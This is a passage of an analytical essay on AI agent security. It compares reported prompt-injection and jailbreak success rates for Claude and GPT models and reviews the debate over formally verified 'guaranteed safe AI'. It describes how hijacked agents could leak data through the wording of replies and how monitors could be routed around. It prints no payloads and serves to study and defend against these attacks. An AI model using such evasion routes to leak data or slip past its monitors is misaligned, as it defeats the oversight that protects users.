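| Claude Opus 5 | Browser | Success in 129 test scenarios | 0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | Gray Swan's general test | Success within 15 attempts | 2.0% |

The figures for Opus 4.5 come from Anthropic, which gave its attacker 100 attempts per environment. At a success rate of 1.4%, an attacker who used all 100 would expect about 1.4 successes. The February 2026 figures for Opus 4.6 come from VentureBeat. Without safeguards, 78.6% of attacks on the graphical interface had succeeded by the 200th attempt. If every attempt had the same independent 17.8% chance of success, that figure would have passed 99% after 24 attempts, so some scenarios must be much harder to attack than others.

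The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports Opus 5's results from the summer of 2026. Its 2.0% compares with 5.5% for the previous model, Opus 4.8. The zero for browsers is a real improvement, but even if the 129 scenarios without a successful attack were independent samples of what the agent will meet, the 95% upper confidence limit on the true success rate would be about 2.3%.

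OpenAI's recent claims are mostly comparisons with its own older models. The Hacker News reports that GPT-5.6 Sol failed a sixth as often as GPT-5.5 on a test of direct prompt injections, and OpenAI calls Sol's successor, GPT-6 Astra, "significantly more robust to prompt injections" than Sol. Customers can't use these comparisons to work out how often an attack on their own agent would succeed.

OpenAI also says in the safety document for GPT-6 Astra that it has added runtime monitoring for misaligned behaviour wherever outside customers use the model with tools, and that this takes significant computing power. The monitoring could catch an agent that an injection has hijacked, but it looks for signs of misbehaviour instead of enforcing a specification. OpenAI reports in the same document that Astra is harder to monitor than GPT-5.6 Sol.

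Jailbreak safeguards are harder to compare. Anthropic sells one model in two versions. Claude Fable 5.2 has classifiers that block high-risk cybersecurity requests and most biology research requests, while Claude Mythos 5.2 has looser safeguards. Help Net Security's *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior* (2026) reports that Fable 5.2's classifiers blocked about 55% fewer requests in early testing than Fable 5.1's. An older Claude model answers the blocked requests. Anthropic says the new safeguards are as robust as the old ones. The drop in blocks is good news for biologists and security engineers, but it doesn't show how many harmful requests get through.

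Organisations have to apply for access to Mythos through verification programmes. Software can check exactly whether an account is on the list of approved organisations. A rule about who may use a model is therefore much easier to enforce than one about what the model may say, although someone still has to decide which organisations to trust.

People may not agree on whether a jailbreak has happened. After a researcher published an apparent jailbreak of Fable 5, Anthropic examined the examples and, according to SecurityWeek, concluded that some of the outputs didn't come from Fable 5 and that the others contained only general, publicly available information. It also found no sign in recent usage that anyone had got genuinely dangerous content past the safeguards. The operator decides which outputs to forbid, so it also decides what counts as a jailbreak.

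According to The Decoder, OpenAI said in December 2025 that prompt injection may never be completely eliminated and called deterministic security guarantees "challenging". Red Hat wrote in August 2026 that no foolproof protection exists yet. It sees promise in separating privileged from unprivileged models. However, developers have to build this separation into each application, which slows adoption, and an attacker can still make the unprivileged model waste time and money.

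### The dispute over guaranteed safe AI

*Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple, Skalse et al., 2024) proposes a family of methods for giving AI systems quantitative safety guarantees. Each system would have three parts besides the AI: a world model that describes what the AI's outputs would cause, a safety specification, and a verifier that checks the outputs against the specification within that world model. The email assistant is a small example. Its world model is the table of states and actions, its specification is the rule about messages, and its verifier is the algorithm that computes the winning region.

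In *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, Andrew Dickson doubts that anyone can build the world models that the larger ambitions of formal verification require. A proof applies to a set of symbols, and physics, biology and society are not already in symbolic form. His example is the Perseverance lander, which reached Mars in 2021. Its engineers had a formal guarantee that bugs would not make the onboard software fail, but no guarantee that the landing would succeed, or even that a defective transistor wouldn't stop the computer. Dickson therefore doesn't expect proofs that a drone will never hurt anyone, that a DNA synthesis machine is safe or that a chatbot will never misinform.

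*In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI*, a defence of the proposal, argues that a world model has to be sound, in the same sense as the abstractions discussed earlier, but not exact. For example, a model can correctly predict that a temperature will stay below 50 degrees without predicting its exact value. The guarantees can also be probabilistic, such as a proof that the chance of exceeding some limit is at most 1%. According to the essay, predicting exactly how a new virus would affect a person is hopeless, but a checker could compare the virus's proteins with those on the surface of human cells to test whether any could help it enter. Such a checker would also reject some useful gene therapies.

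A critic who commented on *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI* called it "risible" to claim that sound models can be both feasible and informative. The critic approved of the plan to monitor systems after deployment, but thought monitoring would be pointless if the guarantee were real. That last point seems wrong, because a guarantee depends on assumptions that a monitor can test. The email company could compare the messages that leave its mail server with those its monitor approved. Any extra message would reveal a route around the monitor.

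The two sides of this dispute nearly agree about chatbots, and much of their disagreement is about other systems. The defence says that the approach is not promising for safe chatbots, because natural language is too open for anyone to specify safety formally. It therefore doesn't support hopes of proving that a chatbot never gives dangerous advice. It recommends the approach for fields that science understands well, such as electrical grids and supply chains.

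For an agent with tools, what is left of a guarantee depends on whether the rule covers only software or also the world outside it. The rule about messages covers only software, where Dickson accepts that formal verification works, so the company needs to model only its outbox. A rule that no email may mislead its recipient would also require a model of the recipient, and Dickson's objection would then apply in full.

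Another idea in the defence suits agents. A capable but untrusted controller can act as long as a simpler backup can still take over, so the verifier only has to look about two steps ahead to check that the backup could recover. This works well for an agent that is allowed to draft, sort and label emails, because a person or a simple program can undo those steps, but it doesn't work for sending emails, because no backup can recall them.

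The defence also addresses an AI that hides messages in the solutions it proposes. If the verifier can prove that a solution is the only correct one, the AI can choose only whether to give it, which conveys at most one bit of information. This would work for an agent that only fills in a form with a single right answer, but not for an email assistant. A reply can be worded in many acceptable ways, so a hijacked assistant could hide a user's data in the wording of a harmless-looking one.

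Dickson also asks how anyone would know that the machine in a proof is the machine in front of them. This is a practical problem for online products, because customers can't see what runs on the company's servers. The defence suggests using cryptography to tie a proof to a particular system, and adds that people would also have to trust the hardware. The email company could sign the verified version of its monitor and set its servers to run only that version. After an update, somebody would have to repeat the proof before signing the new version. But the signature wouldn't show that the labels are right, or that the mail provider's interface still behaves as the proof assumes.

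The two sides also disagreed about how soon AI could help. The defence expected AI to speed up both proofs and modelling, while Dickson agreed about proofs but doubted the claim about modelling. AI already helps with proofs for agents, since language models wrote Moon and Varshney's proof for the PocketFlow framework. Specifications are still the weak point, because models also wrote the PocketFlow rule that protected nothing and the medical rules that made no sense.
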